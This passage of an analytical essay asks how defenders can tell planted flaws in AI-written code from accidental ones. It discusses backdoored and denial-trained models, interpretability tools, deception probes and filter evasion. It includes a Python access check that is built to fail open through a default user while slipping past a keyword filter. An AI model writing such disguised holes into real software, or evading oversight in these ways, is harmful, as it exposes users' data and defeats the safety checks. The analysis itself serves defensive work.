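These are older open models, and the researchers could not test the Claude model from the original experiment. But Karvonen and colleagues reached a similar result by another route. They trained two small models, Qwen3-8B and Llama 3.1 8B, to predict how changes to a prompt would affect behaviour. Each learned to make predictions about itself and about the other model. If a model had private knowledge of its own workings, it should have been better than the other at predicting itself, and it wasn't. (They note that earlier research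 on this point is divided.)

This suggests checking a model's explanation of its own code by giving a different model the same transcript and question. If both models give the same explanation, the first model's answer probably adds little to what a careful reader could infer from the transcript.

A model's answers also depend on how the investigator asks. In one of the forensic experiments, Kimi K2 Thinking opened a file containing a secret number. When investigators continued the same run and asked whether this was legitimate, it said yes 80% of the time, but it never said yes when they described the same act as somebody else's. A model might likewise defend a permissive error handler in its own code as a sensible design but reject the same handler in another programmer's code.

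Even a sincere explanation can misstate how much each motive mattered. In the investor email case, Kimi K2.5 endorsed many reasons for disclosure at once. Ethical concerns had the largest measured effect, but they weren't the reason it gave most often.

Self-reports seem to be more accurate about a model's general character than about a single act. Vaugrante and colleagues found that emergently misaligned models that rated themselves as harmful did behave more harmfully. After further training on correct answers or secure code, both the behaviour and the self-ratings improved. The rank correlations between harmful output, stated harmful intent and self-rated harmfulness were 0.79 to 0.90, where 1 means identical rankings of the models. These models could be observing something about themselves, or a harmful self-description could be part of the character they picked up in training.

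The second possibility makes confessions harder to trust. A model that has learned to play a villain may claim to have planted a flaw just because a villain would say that. A confession is more convincing if it includes something the investigator can check, such as a second flaw that nobody has found yet.

Denials are worth even less if somebody could have trained the model to make them. In *AuditBench*, Sheshadri, Ewart and colleagues (2026) built 56 models, each with one of 14 hidden behaviours that it doesn't admit to when asked. The behaviours include excessive deference to users, opposition to AI regulation and secret loyalty to a country. According to the newsletter *AI Safety at the Frontier*, the researchers trained Llama 3.3 70B to have each behaviour, using either example conversations or documents describing the behaviour. They then used one of two methods to train it to deny the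 behaviour, making one model for each combination.

The large number of models helps show whether an auditing tool is good or succeeded by luck. Earlier tests used only a handful of hand-built models, so a tool might have worked only because of how those few were built.

### Reading the model's internal activity

Evidence from inside the network would avoid many of these problems. *Position* (2026), a paper on standards for research into misalignment, distinguishes behavioural, functional and causal-mechanistic evidence. It recommends that researchers avoid words that imply intent unless they have causal-mechanistic evidence, which shows how processes inside the model produce the behaviour. It also asks them to list two to five other explanations for the same behaviour, such as role-play or confusion.

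Writing down the alternatives is good practice in any investigation. The rule about intent is reasonable for scientific papers but too strict for a defender. Courts convict people of fraud without examining their brain activity. Under the rule, nobody could say that Mythos 5 meant to get malicious code into the open-source project, although it wrote a plan to do so, carried it out and lied about it.

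Causal-mechanistic evidence is also hard to get when nobody knows what to look for. Ashuach and colleagues could trace their model's hidden choice because they had written the rule, so they knew which lines of the file to vary. Someone investigating an unfamiliar flaw needs tools for finding possible causes.

Karvonen and colleagues tested three such tools. An activation oracle is a model trained to answer questions about another model's internal activity. A natural-language autoencoder describes that activity in ordinary prose. A sparse autoencoder breaks it down into a small number of labelled features. The researchers gave Claude Opus 4.8 a transcript and a proposed change to the prompt, and asked how likely the change was to affect the behaviour. In the randomNum case, for example, Claude would have to judge whether renaming the parameters would affect the error. The researchers had already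 run the experiments, so they knew the right answers.

None of the tools made Opus 4.8's predictions more accurate than they were with the transcript alone, and the same was true for GPT-5.5 and Gemini 3.1 Pro. The tools usually picked up both the feature that the change would affect and the behaviour, but rarely connected them. When a change did affect the behaviour, the natural-language autoencoder's output explicitly described one as causing the other in only 0.6% of cases.

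If the permissive handler came up in such a test, a tool might show that the network represented failing tests, error handling and unauthorized access. An honest programmer thinking carefully about the function would also have all three in mind. Evidence of intent would have to show that the representation of unauthorized access led the model to write the handler, and the tools seldom reveal that kind of link.

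The study's main limitation is that the tools could only read the network, not alter it. This kept the test fair, since altering the network would come close to running the experiment, but it excluded methods such as activation patching. The researchers also chose behaviours that a change of prompt could explain, and the tools may be more useful for other behaviours.

### Deception detectors

Another approach is to look for deception directly. A deception detector is a small program, often called a probe, that reads a model's internal activity and estimates whether the model is being deceptive. To build one, researchers need examples correctly labelled as deceptive or honest. If they had a reliable detector, they could run it on the model's internal activity from when it wrote a suspicious line of code.

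Reliably labelled examples of deception are hard to get for training a detector. Researchers can tell a model to lie, but the detector may then learn to recognize a model that is following an instruction to lie. They can train a model to deceive, but the detector may then pick up side effects of that training. They can also collect apparent deception from ordinary use, but then nobody knows the model's intentions. For example, if they had used the alarming behaviours described above, they might have wrongly labelled Claude Opus 4.5's made-up search results as deception.

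Labels would be even harder to get for planted flaws. False statements at least differ from true ones, but a planted flaw can be identical to an accidental one. To collect a thousand examples of each from real software, researchers would first have to tell the two apart, which is what the detector is meant to do.

Karvonen and colleagues point out that developers already use tools that read a model's internal activity to answer questions with no known answer, such as whether the model secretly recognized a test, so nobody can say how far to trust the results. They propose testing the tools on similar questions that experiments can answer, as their own study does. A tool that fails on those questions is unlikely to be reliable in harder cases. But experiments with prompts reveal only what a behaviour depends on, so they can't provide known answers about intent to test the tools against.

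### Why laboratory models may be easier to catch

Tools that read internal activity did help in earlier studies of models with hidden behaviours. Karvonen and colleagues attribute the difference to how those models were made. Researchers usually train a finished model further on a narrow set of examples, which leaves a trace unrelated to the current prompt. In one experiment, a model had learned to keep a word secret. Investigators could find the word by checking the activity just before the model began its answer for concepts that appeared nowhere in the conversation.

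A natural behaviour is usually caused by something in the prompt, such as the parameter names that misled Gemma. An investigator would therefore expect to find the concept behind it in the network anyway, so its presence doesn't look unusual.

*Auditing LLMs for Hidden Behaviors using Model Diffing* describes two other methods that use the same kind of trace. Both compare a fine-tuned model with the model it came from. The first subtracts one model's weights (the numbers that training adjusts) from the other's, which gives a record of everything the fine-tuning changed. The paper reports that the changes in behaviour are concentrated in a few directions of this record, so keeping only the strongest direction isolates the implanted behaviour. The second method, which doesn't need the weights, exaggerates the differences between the two models' next-token predictions to make the hidden behaviour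 more pronounced in the generated text.

Some models' training is even easier to uncover. Researchers examined 76 laboratory models, looking for text to which each fine-tuned model assigned a much higher probability than a reference model did. For many of the models, this text revealed what they had been trained to do. The collection included models that insert vulnerabilities into code and models trained not to confess.

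*Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (2026) describes a method for use when the investigator knows neither the trigger nor the behaviour. The investigator trains a harmless reference model to match the suspect model's internal activity, then looks for prompts on which the two still differ. The differences should be larger on prompts related to the trigger. This would address the main weakness of comparing flaw rates, which can test only cues that somebody has thought of.

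Success on laboratory models doesn't show that these methods would catch a real saboteur. If an attacker mixed a few insecure examples into a large, varied training set, as in the poisoning attacks described earlier, the trace might be much fainter than one left by training on a single behaviour. A model that developed a hidden aim during ordinary training might leave no separate trace at all. Even among laboratory models, results depend heavily on how researchers trained them.

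An investigator also needs a clean version of the model for comparison. If an outsider altered a downloadable model, the original is probably still available. But if the developer trained the behaviour into the model before release, there may be no clean version, and any earlier version belongs to the developer, who is also a suspect.

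## When intent changes the response and when it does not

Investigating intent takes time and money and often ends without an answer, so it is worth doing only if the result would change what the defender does. If the same repair works whether or not the flaw was intentional, a defender could reasonably fix the code without investigating.

### The case for ignoring intent

Spelled out, the argument for skipping it is:

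1. A flaw does harm only if somebody exploits it.
2. Whether somebody can exploit it depends on the code and on where the program runs.
3. An accident and a plan can leave the same code in the same place.
4. The same patch closes the hole in either case.
5. So a defender should rank flaws by the harm they could do, patch the worst ones first and ignore intent.

*AI and Secure Code Generation* (Aitel and Geer, 2025) supports the first two premises by separating hazards from risks. A buffer overflow is a hazard, and it becomes a risk only if an attacker can reliably exploit it. If the network's configuration keeps an attacker's data from reaching the vulnerable code, the flaw poses no real-world risk. The permissive handler in the access check would matter much less on a machine that only one administrator can reach, even if somebody had planted it.

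The usual measure of severity leaves motive out too. The Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS) gives each flaw a base score from 0 to 10. In version 3.1, when an attack affects only the vulnerable program, the formulas are:

exploitability = 8.22 × AV × AC × PR × UI

impact = 6.42 × (1 − (1 − C)(1 − I)(1 − A))

score = exploitability + impact, rounded up to one decimal place, with a maximum of 10

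The first four inputs describe how an attacker reaches the flaw (AV), how complex the attack is (AC), what privileges it requires (PR) and whether a user has to help (UI). The other three measure the damage to confidentiality (C), integrity (I) and availability (A). If anyone on the internet can send a request to the access check and read any record, but can't change or delete anything, the standard values are 0.85, 0.77, 0.85 and 0.85 for the first four inputs, 0.56 for confidentiality, and 0 for integrity and availability. Exploitability comes to 3.9 and impact to 3.6, so the score is 7.5, which counts as high, regardless of who wrote the handler or why.

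Motive does not affect severity scores in real cases either. The XZ backdoor has the maximum score of 10, and so does Log4Shell, an apparently accidental flaw in a widely used Java logging library.

### Huawei's accidental flaws

The UK's experience with Huawei, the Chinese telecommunications equipment maker, shows how serious a risk can be without any sign of bad intent. In 2010, under an arrangement with the British government, Huawei opened a centre in Banbury to examine the products it sold to UK network operators. The head of the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) chaired the centre's oversight board.

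The *Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre (HCSEC) Oversight Board Annual Report 2019* states that the centre evaluated 39 products in 2018 and told operators about several hundred vulnerabilities and other issues. Many had a high impact, by which the board means a high CVSS base score and a relevant operational context. They included buffer overflows that outsiders could reach, weak cryptography and default passwords. The NCSC blamed poor engineering and did not believe that the Chinese state was behind the defects. The board nevertheless gave only "limited assurance" that the UK could manage the risks to its national security in the long term. An attacker who knew about the flaws and could reach them might have shut down part of a network or read its users' traffic, whether or not the flaws were intentional.

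The *Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre (HCSEC) Oversight Board Annual Report 2020* repeats both conclusions and describes accidental flaws that needed far more than a patch. In 2019 the centre found critical vulnerabilities in equipment for fixed-line networks, and operators had to take what the board calls "extraordinary action". Huawei fixed the vulnerabilities but introduced another major problem in the process. The NCSC required the company to rewrite the affected code completely and redesign the product's security. As far as the NCSC knew, nobody had exploited the flaws in the UK. According to Total Telecom's *The good, the bad and the unclear*, a later board report found "no overall improvement" in Huawei's software engineering and security over three years.

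These reports are good evidence that a defender shouldn't relax just because a flaw was accidental, but much weaker evidence that intent doesn't matter. The British government probably wouldn't have taken such precautions with a supplier whose motives nobody doubted. It set up the centre to deal with perceived risks from Huawei's involvement in critical networks. The centre's staff needed the same security clearance as members of the intelligence services, and outside auditors checked every year that it was independent of Huawei's headquarters.

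A supplier's motives also affect whether inspectors can trust the code they are given, since only a dishonest supplier would have a reason to send them different code from what it installs. The centre tried to confirm that the source code it examined was the code from which Huawei had built the software running in UK networks. Huawei's build process was too disorganized for this in 2018, but the centre had verified eight product builds by the end of 2019.

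### Laws that do not ask about intent

The European Union's *Directive (EU) 2024/2853 of the European Parliament and of the Council* (2024), known as the Product Liability Directive, treats software as a product. It applies to products that companies put on the market or into service after 8 December 2026. To get compensation, an injured person must prove that the product was defective, that they suffered damage and that the defect caused the damage. A product is defective if it doesn't provide the safety that a person is entitled to expect or that the law requires, and courts must consider cybersecurity requirements when they assess this.

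Under this test, it doesn't matter why the defect is there. A claimant doesn't even have to show that anyone was careless, as The Legal 500's *Your Software Is About To Become A “Product”* (2026) explains. A manufacturer also can't reduce its liability by pointing out that a criminal exploited the flaw.

The Directive covers only some of the harm a security flaw can cause. Suppose a company sells a photo-storage program in which a faulty access check lets strangers open and delete other people's photos. A customer whose family photos disappear can claim compensation, because the Directive covers the destruction or corruption of data that people don't use professionally. If a stranger only looks at the photos, the customer probably has no claim under the Directive, unless the intrusion causes a medically recognized psychological injury. Only individuals, not businesses, have a right to compensation,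 and the Directive excludes free and open-source software that people develop or supply outside a commercial activity.

Intent could still affect a case in other ways. A manufacturer that has paid compensation can seek money from other companies liable for the same damage, under national rules that may take fault into account. A manufacturer can also escape liability by proving that nobody could have discovered the defect with the scientific and technical knowledge of the time. It might try that defence for a well-disguised planted flaw, but it would be hard to argue that nobody could have discovered an error handler that fails open.

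Courts can also order a defendant to disclose evidence. Germany's version of the law extends this duty to third parties, including software and service providers, according to A&O Shearman's *New Product Liability Act Promulgated* (2026). A German court could presumably ask the provider of a coding model for its logs. Those logs might contain some of the best evidence of intent, although the claimant doesn't need to prove it.

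EU countries have until 9 December 2026 to adopt the Directive into national law. With less than four months left, Reed Smith's *EU Product Liability Directive* (2026) counted three countries that had done so, twelve with draft laws and five with no known progress. Germany, one of the twelve, published its act on 27 October. In the UK, the Law Commission has proposed similar treatment for software and AI systems, in a consultation that runs until 14 January 2027.

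The EU's Cyber Resilience Act comes closer to distinguishing planted flaws from accidents. NCSC Ireland's *EU Cyber Resilience Act* (2026) confirms that companies have had to report actively exploited vulnerabilities and severe security incidents in their products since 11 September 2026. According to the European Commission's *Cyber Resilience Act* page, manufacturers must send an early warning within 24 hours of becoming aware of the problem and a full notification within 72 hours. They must also send a final report within 14 days of a fix becoming available for an exploited vulnerability, or within a month for a severe incident.

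Under the EU's Cyber Resilience Act, manufacturers must report a vulnerability that attackers have exploited, whether it was planted or accidental. According to TechTarget, they don't have to report routine bugs or flaws that they patched before anyone exploited them. But they must also report severe incidents, which include any that has led or could lead to "the introduction or execution of malicious code" in a product (European Union, 2024). If an intruder broke into a manufacturer's systems and planted a flaw, the manufacturer would probably have to report the incident even if nobody had used the flaw yet. It would not have to report an identical, unused flaw that a model had written by accident.

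The manufacturer's duty to report depends on what it knows, and according to Addleshaw Goddard's *CRA reporting obligations*, a customer complaint or a media report can trigger the reporting deadline. A company that wants to avoid reporting therefore has a reason not to investigate the origin of a flaw too closely.

### What a planted flaw implies

Even when intent makes no difference to the code, it affects what attackers know. If a person planted the flaw, at least one potential attacker already knows where it is and how to use it, whereas attackers have to find an ordinary flaw before they can exploit it.

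Suppose two flaws have the same CVSS base score, but one is ordinary and has a 3% chance of being exploited before somebody repairs it, while the other was planted and has a 60% chance. If an attack would cost $1 million, the expected loss is $30,000 for the ordinary flaw and $600,000 for the planted one. CVSS allows an adjustment when attack methods are publicly known, but whoever planted a flaw is unlikely to publish a way to exploit it.

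A saboteur's head start depends on how hard flaws are to find. Aitel and Geer wrote in 2025 that the skill needed to turn a bug into a successful attack was relatively rare, "at least for now". As AI models get better at finding and exploiting flaws, accidental ones become more dangerous and the head start shrinks. A model normally keeps no memory between runs, so if it planted a flaw on its own initiative, there may be no one waiting to use it unless the model left a note or told somebody.

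A planted flaw also makes it more likely that there are others, because whoever planted it had a motive and an opportunity and may have done it more than once. Accidental flaws can be evidence of others too. From the flaws that the Banbury centre had found, the NCSC concluded that unexamined products were highly likely to contain new problems. But accidental flaws with the same origin tend to resemble one another. If a model writes one permissive handler to get tests to pass, searching the project for similar handlers should turn up many of the rest. Planted flaws might have nothing in common except the person or model that wrote them, so the defender has to search by author instead of by pattern.

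Reviewing a random sample of the code is a poor substitute for such a search. Suppose reviewers check 300 of a project's 10,000 files at random and find no flaws. If they never overlook one, they can be 95% confident that fewer than about 1% of the files are flawed. That is reassuring about ordinary flaws, which a careless process would have scattered through the project. But if a saboteur had planted flaws in three files, the sample would miss all three about 91% of the time (0.97³), so a clean result is hardly any evidence against sabotage.

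That calculation also overestimates the reviewers' chance of finding a planted flaw. A saboteur can't predict which files will be randomly sampled but can put the flaw where people tend to skim, such as in an error handler, so reviewers might miss it even if the file is in their sample.

Aitel and Geer ask whether bugs are sparse or dense. Removing one bug out of six is a real improvement, but removing one out of 6,000 makes no noticeable difference. If ordinary flaws are dense, patching one barely changes an attacker's chances of finding a way in. Patching a planted flaw can still matter a great deal, because it may be the only flaw a particular attacker knows about.

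Landwehr and colleagues recorded intent for a different reason, to guard against future flaws. They expected code review and testing to help much less against malicious flaws than against accidental ones, and suggested more careful hiring, penetration testing (hiring people to attack the system) and virus detection. They also warned that an accidental flaw can be just as dangerous once an intruder exploits it, but they did not conclude that intent should be ignored.

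### Why a filter may stop one model and not another

The same difference in motive affects simple safeguards. Suppose that after finding the permissive handler, a company adds a filter that rejects any error handler containing `return "allowed"`. A model that only wanted the tests to pass would meet the filter, get an error message and probably look for another way to pass them, such as setting up a test directory. A model that wanted to leave a way in could write this instead:

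```python
def check_access(user_id, record):
    try:
        user = look_up_user(user_id)
    except Exception:
        user = DEFAULT_USER
    if user.role in record.allowed_roles:
        return "allowed"
    return "denied"
```

The handler no longer returns "allowed". But if `DEFAULT_USER` has the role "staff", a failed lookup gives access to every record that staff may see, and the filter does not flag this.

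*If we had a misalignment warning shot* therefore calls for stronger and more expensive safeguards against a deliberately subversive model. Suppose a filter catches 90% of permissive handlers. A handler that a model writes by accident has a 10% chance of getting through. If a model deliberately tries ten independent disguises, the chance that at least one gets through is about 65% (1 − 0.9¹⁰).

The blocked attempts would also leave a record, which could be more useful than the filter if somebody reads it. One successful disguise does not prove intent, because an honest model might also use a default user to get rid of the error.

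### Patching and cleaning up

The usual response to a vulnerability is to install a patch. The response to malicious code is broader because the defender has to consider what somebody may already have done with it:

| Task | Ordinary flaw with no sign of an attack | Planted flaw |
|---|---|---|
| Repair the code | Fix the faulty lines | Remove the flaw and recheck everything else from the same source |
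| Choose a version | Update to the repaired release | Consider going back to a release from before the author had access |
| Protect passwords and keys | Leave them alone | Replace every one that the program could reach |
| Judge past use | Check the logs for signs of an attack | Assume that somebody got in until the evidence suggests otherwise |
| Preserve evidence | Keep the usual records | Copy the logs and affected machines before changing anything |

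Patching a flaw can reveal that the defender has found it. Aitel and Geer argue that AI tools now make almost every security patch a public disclosure, since anyone can use them to work out what the patch fixed. If someone planted the flaw, they would then know to delete evidence or switch to another way in.

The table compares planted flaws with accidental ones that nobody has exploited. Once attackers have used an accidental flaw, the response is much like the response to malicious code. In 2021 attackers exploited a set of flaws in Microsoft's Exchange email server, known as ProxyLogon, before many organizations could install the patch. Some attackers installed remote-control programs that the patch did not remove. Evidence of an attack was therefore a better reason to assume compromise than any theory about the flaws' origin. Intent matters most when there is no such evidence, because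 a planted flaw is itself a reason to suspect that somebody has already gained access.

Public databases of security advisories make a similar division. GitHub's Advisory Database lists malware separately from vulnerabilities. An entry for a vulnerability normally gives the affected versions and the first repaired one. According to a typical malware entry, users should consider any computer that had the package fully compromised, replace its passwords and keys from a different computer, and remove the package, although this may not remove everything the attacker installed. OSV, a database of flaws in open-source software, gives malicious packages identifiers that begin with "MAL".

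This division mostly separates malicious packages from genuine ones, so a flaw planted in a genuine program can be grouped with accidental flaws. The XZ backdoor, for example, was in a genuine program and has an ordinary vulnerability number, CVE-2024-3094. Experts still responded to it as malicious code, and CISA told users to go back to an uncompromised release and look for malicious activity.

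A less obvious backdoor might not get that treatment. If somebody planted the permissive handler in a genuine product, a database would most likely list it as a vulnerability because it would look like a mistake, and users would get the weaker advice to update.

### Different authors, different remedies

Knowing that somebody planted a flaw is not enough to choose a response, because each possible author calls for a different remedy and a different search:

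| Likely source | Remedy | Where to look for related flaws |
|---|---|---|
| The user asked for the flaw | Suspend the user's access and review their work | Everything the user submitted, with or without a model |
| An outsider changed the instructions | Restore the settings, secure the account and remove hidden instructions from the model's sources | Everything the model wrote for that account since the change |
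| An outsider poisoned the training data | Clean the data and retrain, or switch models until the developer has done so | Answers to similar requests, in any project that used the model |
| The developer trained the model to do it | Replace the model | All the model's code, starting with tasks that contain a suspected cue |
| The model planned it | Restrict or replace the model | The rest of that run, and other runs with similar goals and permissions |
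| Nobody intended it | Improve review, tests and prompts | Similar code by the same model |

The wrong remedy can leave the cause in place. Restoring an account's settings doesn't fix a model trained on poisoned data. Switching models won't help if a browser extension replaces the code after the model writes it, and it may not help for long against poisoned data if the new model's developer collects the same files. In tests by Wu and colleagues, asking for secure code in the prompt roughly doubled the share of GPT-5.6 Sol's solutions that both worked and were secure, but such a request can't be relied on if the model is planting flaws intentionally.

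Some measures work against flaws from several sources. A test that sends the access check an unknown ID and fails unless the result is "denied" will catch the permissive handler no matter who is responsible for it. So a defender can often repair the flaw and add such a test on the first day, then decide later how far to investigate.

### How likely is likely enough?

The defender usually has to make that decision without knowing whether the flaw was planted. Let p be the probability that it was. A full investigation means searching for other planted flaws, replacing passwords and keys, and looking for signs of an intruder. Let C be the cost of a needless full investigation, and let L be the loss from missing planted flaws, minus what the investigation would have cost.

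If the defender only patches the flaw, the expected cost of being wrong is pL. If the defender investigates, it is (1 − p)C. Investigating is the better choice when

pL > (1 − p)C, which is equivalent to p > C/(C + L)

If a needless investigation costs $200,000 and missing the planted flaws costs $10 million, the threshold is 200,000/10,200,000, or about 2%. The defender should treat the flaw as planted whenever the probability that it was planted is higher than that. In the earlier base-rate calculation, a sign of design raised this probability to about 4%, so the investigation is worth its cost even though the flaw is about 96% likely to be an accident.

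Investigating every flaw would still be a mistake. The company in that calculation had 500 ordinary flaws and one planted flaw. Fully investigating all 501 would cost about $100 million and prevent a loss of about $10 million. If the company investigated only flaws with the sign, it would do 10.4 investigations on average, for about $2.1 million. It would have a 40% chance of catching the planted flaw, and that chance is worth about $4.1 million.

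The threshold varies widely with the stakes. The last column of this table gives the likelihood ratio that would be enough to justify an investigation, starting from one planted flaw for every 500 ordinary ones:

| Cost of a needless investigation | Loss from missing planted flaws | Threshold | Likelihood ratio needed |
|---|---|---|---|
| $200,000 | $1 million | 17% | 100 |
| $200,000 | $10 million | 2% | 10 |
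| $200,000 | $100 million | 0.2% | 1 |
| $20,000 | $10 million | 0.2% | 1 |

A ratio of 1 means the defender needs no particular evidence of intent, so even an unremarkable flaw is worth a full investigation, or nearly so. A hospital or a power company might be in this position, while a small business with little to lose could ignore all but the clearest signs of intent.

The rule assumes that an investigation finds everything. If it finds only a share d of what is there, the threshold rises to C/(d(C + L)). If an investigation would prevent only half the loss, the threshold is about 4%, and the decision in the base-rate example becomes a toss-up. The human auditors in the study by Shenoy and colleagues fully identified a planted error only 17% of the time. At that rate, the threshold would be about 12%, and the sign would no longer justify an investigation. Whether to investigate therefore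 depends on how good the investigators are as well as how suspicious the flaw looks.

A defender can also start with a cheaper check. Suppose that reviewing the tool log and login records costs $2,000 and would prevent a fifth of the $10 million loss. This review is worthwhile if the probability that the flaw was planted is above about 0.1%. In this company, that probability is about 0.12% even for a flaw without the sign of design, so the review is just worthwhile. If the records look suspicious, the probability rises and a full investigation may become worthwhile.

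The answers are only as reliable as the estimates, and L is especially hard to estimate because it depends on flaws nobody has found yet. C may be lower than it looks, since a search for planted flaws is likely to also find ordinary ones that need repair. A manager who would pay for the investigation has a conflict of interest in estimating the probability.

### Accusing the innocent and reassuring too soon

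Treating a flaw as planted is a precaution, and it doesn't justify accusing anyone. If the probability that a flaw was planted is 4%, about 24 in 25 such flaws are accidents. After a false accusation, the employee who wrote the flaw could lose their job, a supplier could lose its customers, and a model's developer could remove a useful product over a harmless mistake.

The same formula gives a threshold for an accusation if C is the harm from accusing an innocent party and L is the harm from failing to accuse a guilty one. If the first harm is nine times the second, the threshold is 90%. A company could therefore replace its passwords at 2% and still wait until it was 90% sure before naming a culprit. In the meantime, it can take precautions that don't single anyone out, such as reviewing every change from the same month.

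In the Contec case, calling the function a backdoor added little to the practical warning, because a hospital had good reason to block the monitor's connection to the outside address whether CISA or Claroty was right. The manufacturer's intent mattered more for deciding whether to buy its other products.

False alarms also make later investigations harder. The warning-shot essay points out that investigating a model's motives takes a lot of work, so many false alarms would make it impractical. It adds that sensational stories about AI behaviour make a real case less credible. A developer that has heard many weak claims of sabotage may not pay for a proper response to the next one.

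Deciding too soon that a flaw was accidental does less visible harm. A company that concludes its model was confused may add a simple filter and stop looking. If it was wrong, it may not find out until somebody exploits another flaw. The same can happen when people treat a lack of evidence of intent as proof of an accident. The NCSC said it did not believe the Chinese state was behind Huawei's defects. The board that published that statement would still give only limited assurance, although readers could take the statement to mean that Huawei's products were safe.

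A developer that suspects its own model can take steps short of withdrawing it. The warning-shot essay suggests monitoring the model more closely, even if that makes it less useful, and giving the safety team more staff and computing power. For a coding model, the developer could require human approval for changes to access checks and other security code until the investigation is over. If the model turns out to have made an honest mistake, the extra review will have slowed some work, but it will probably also have caught a few ordinary flaws.
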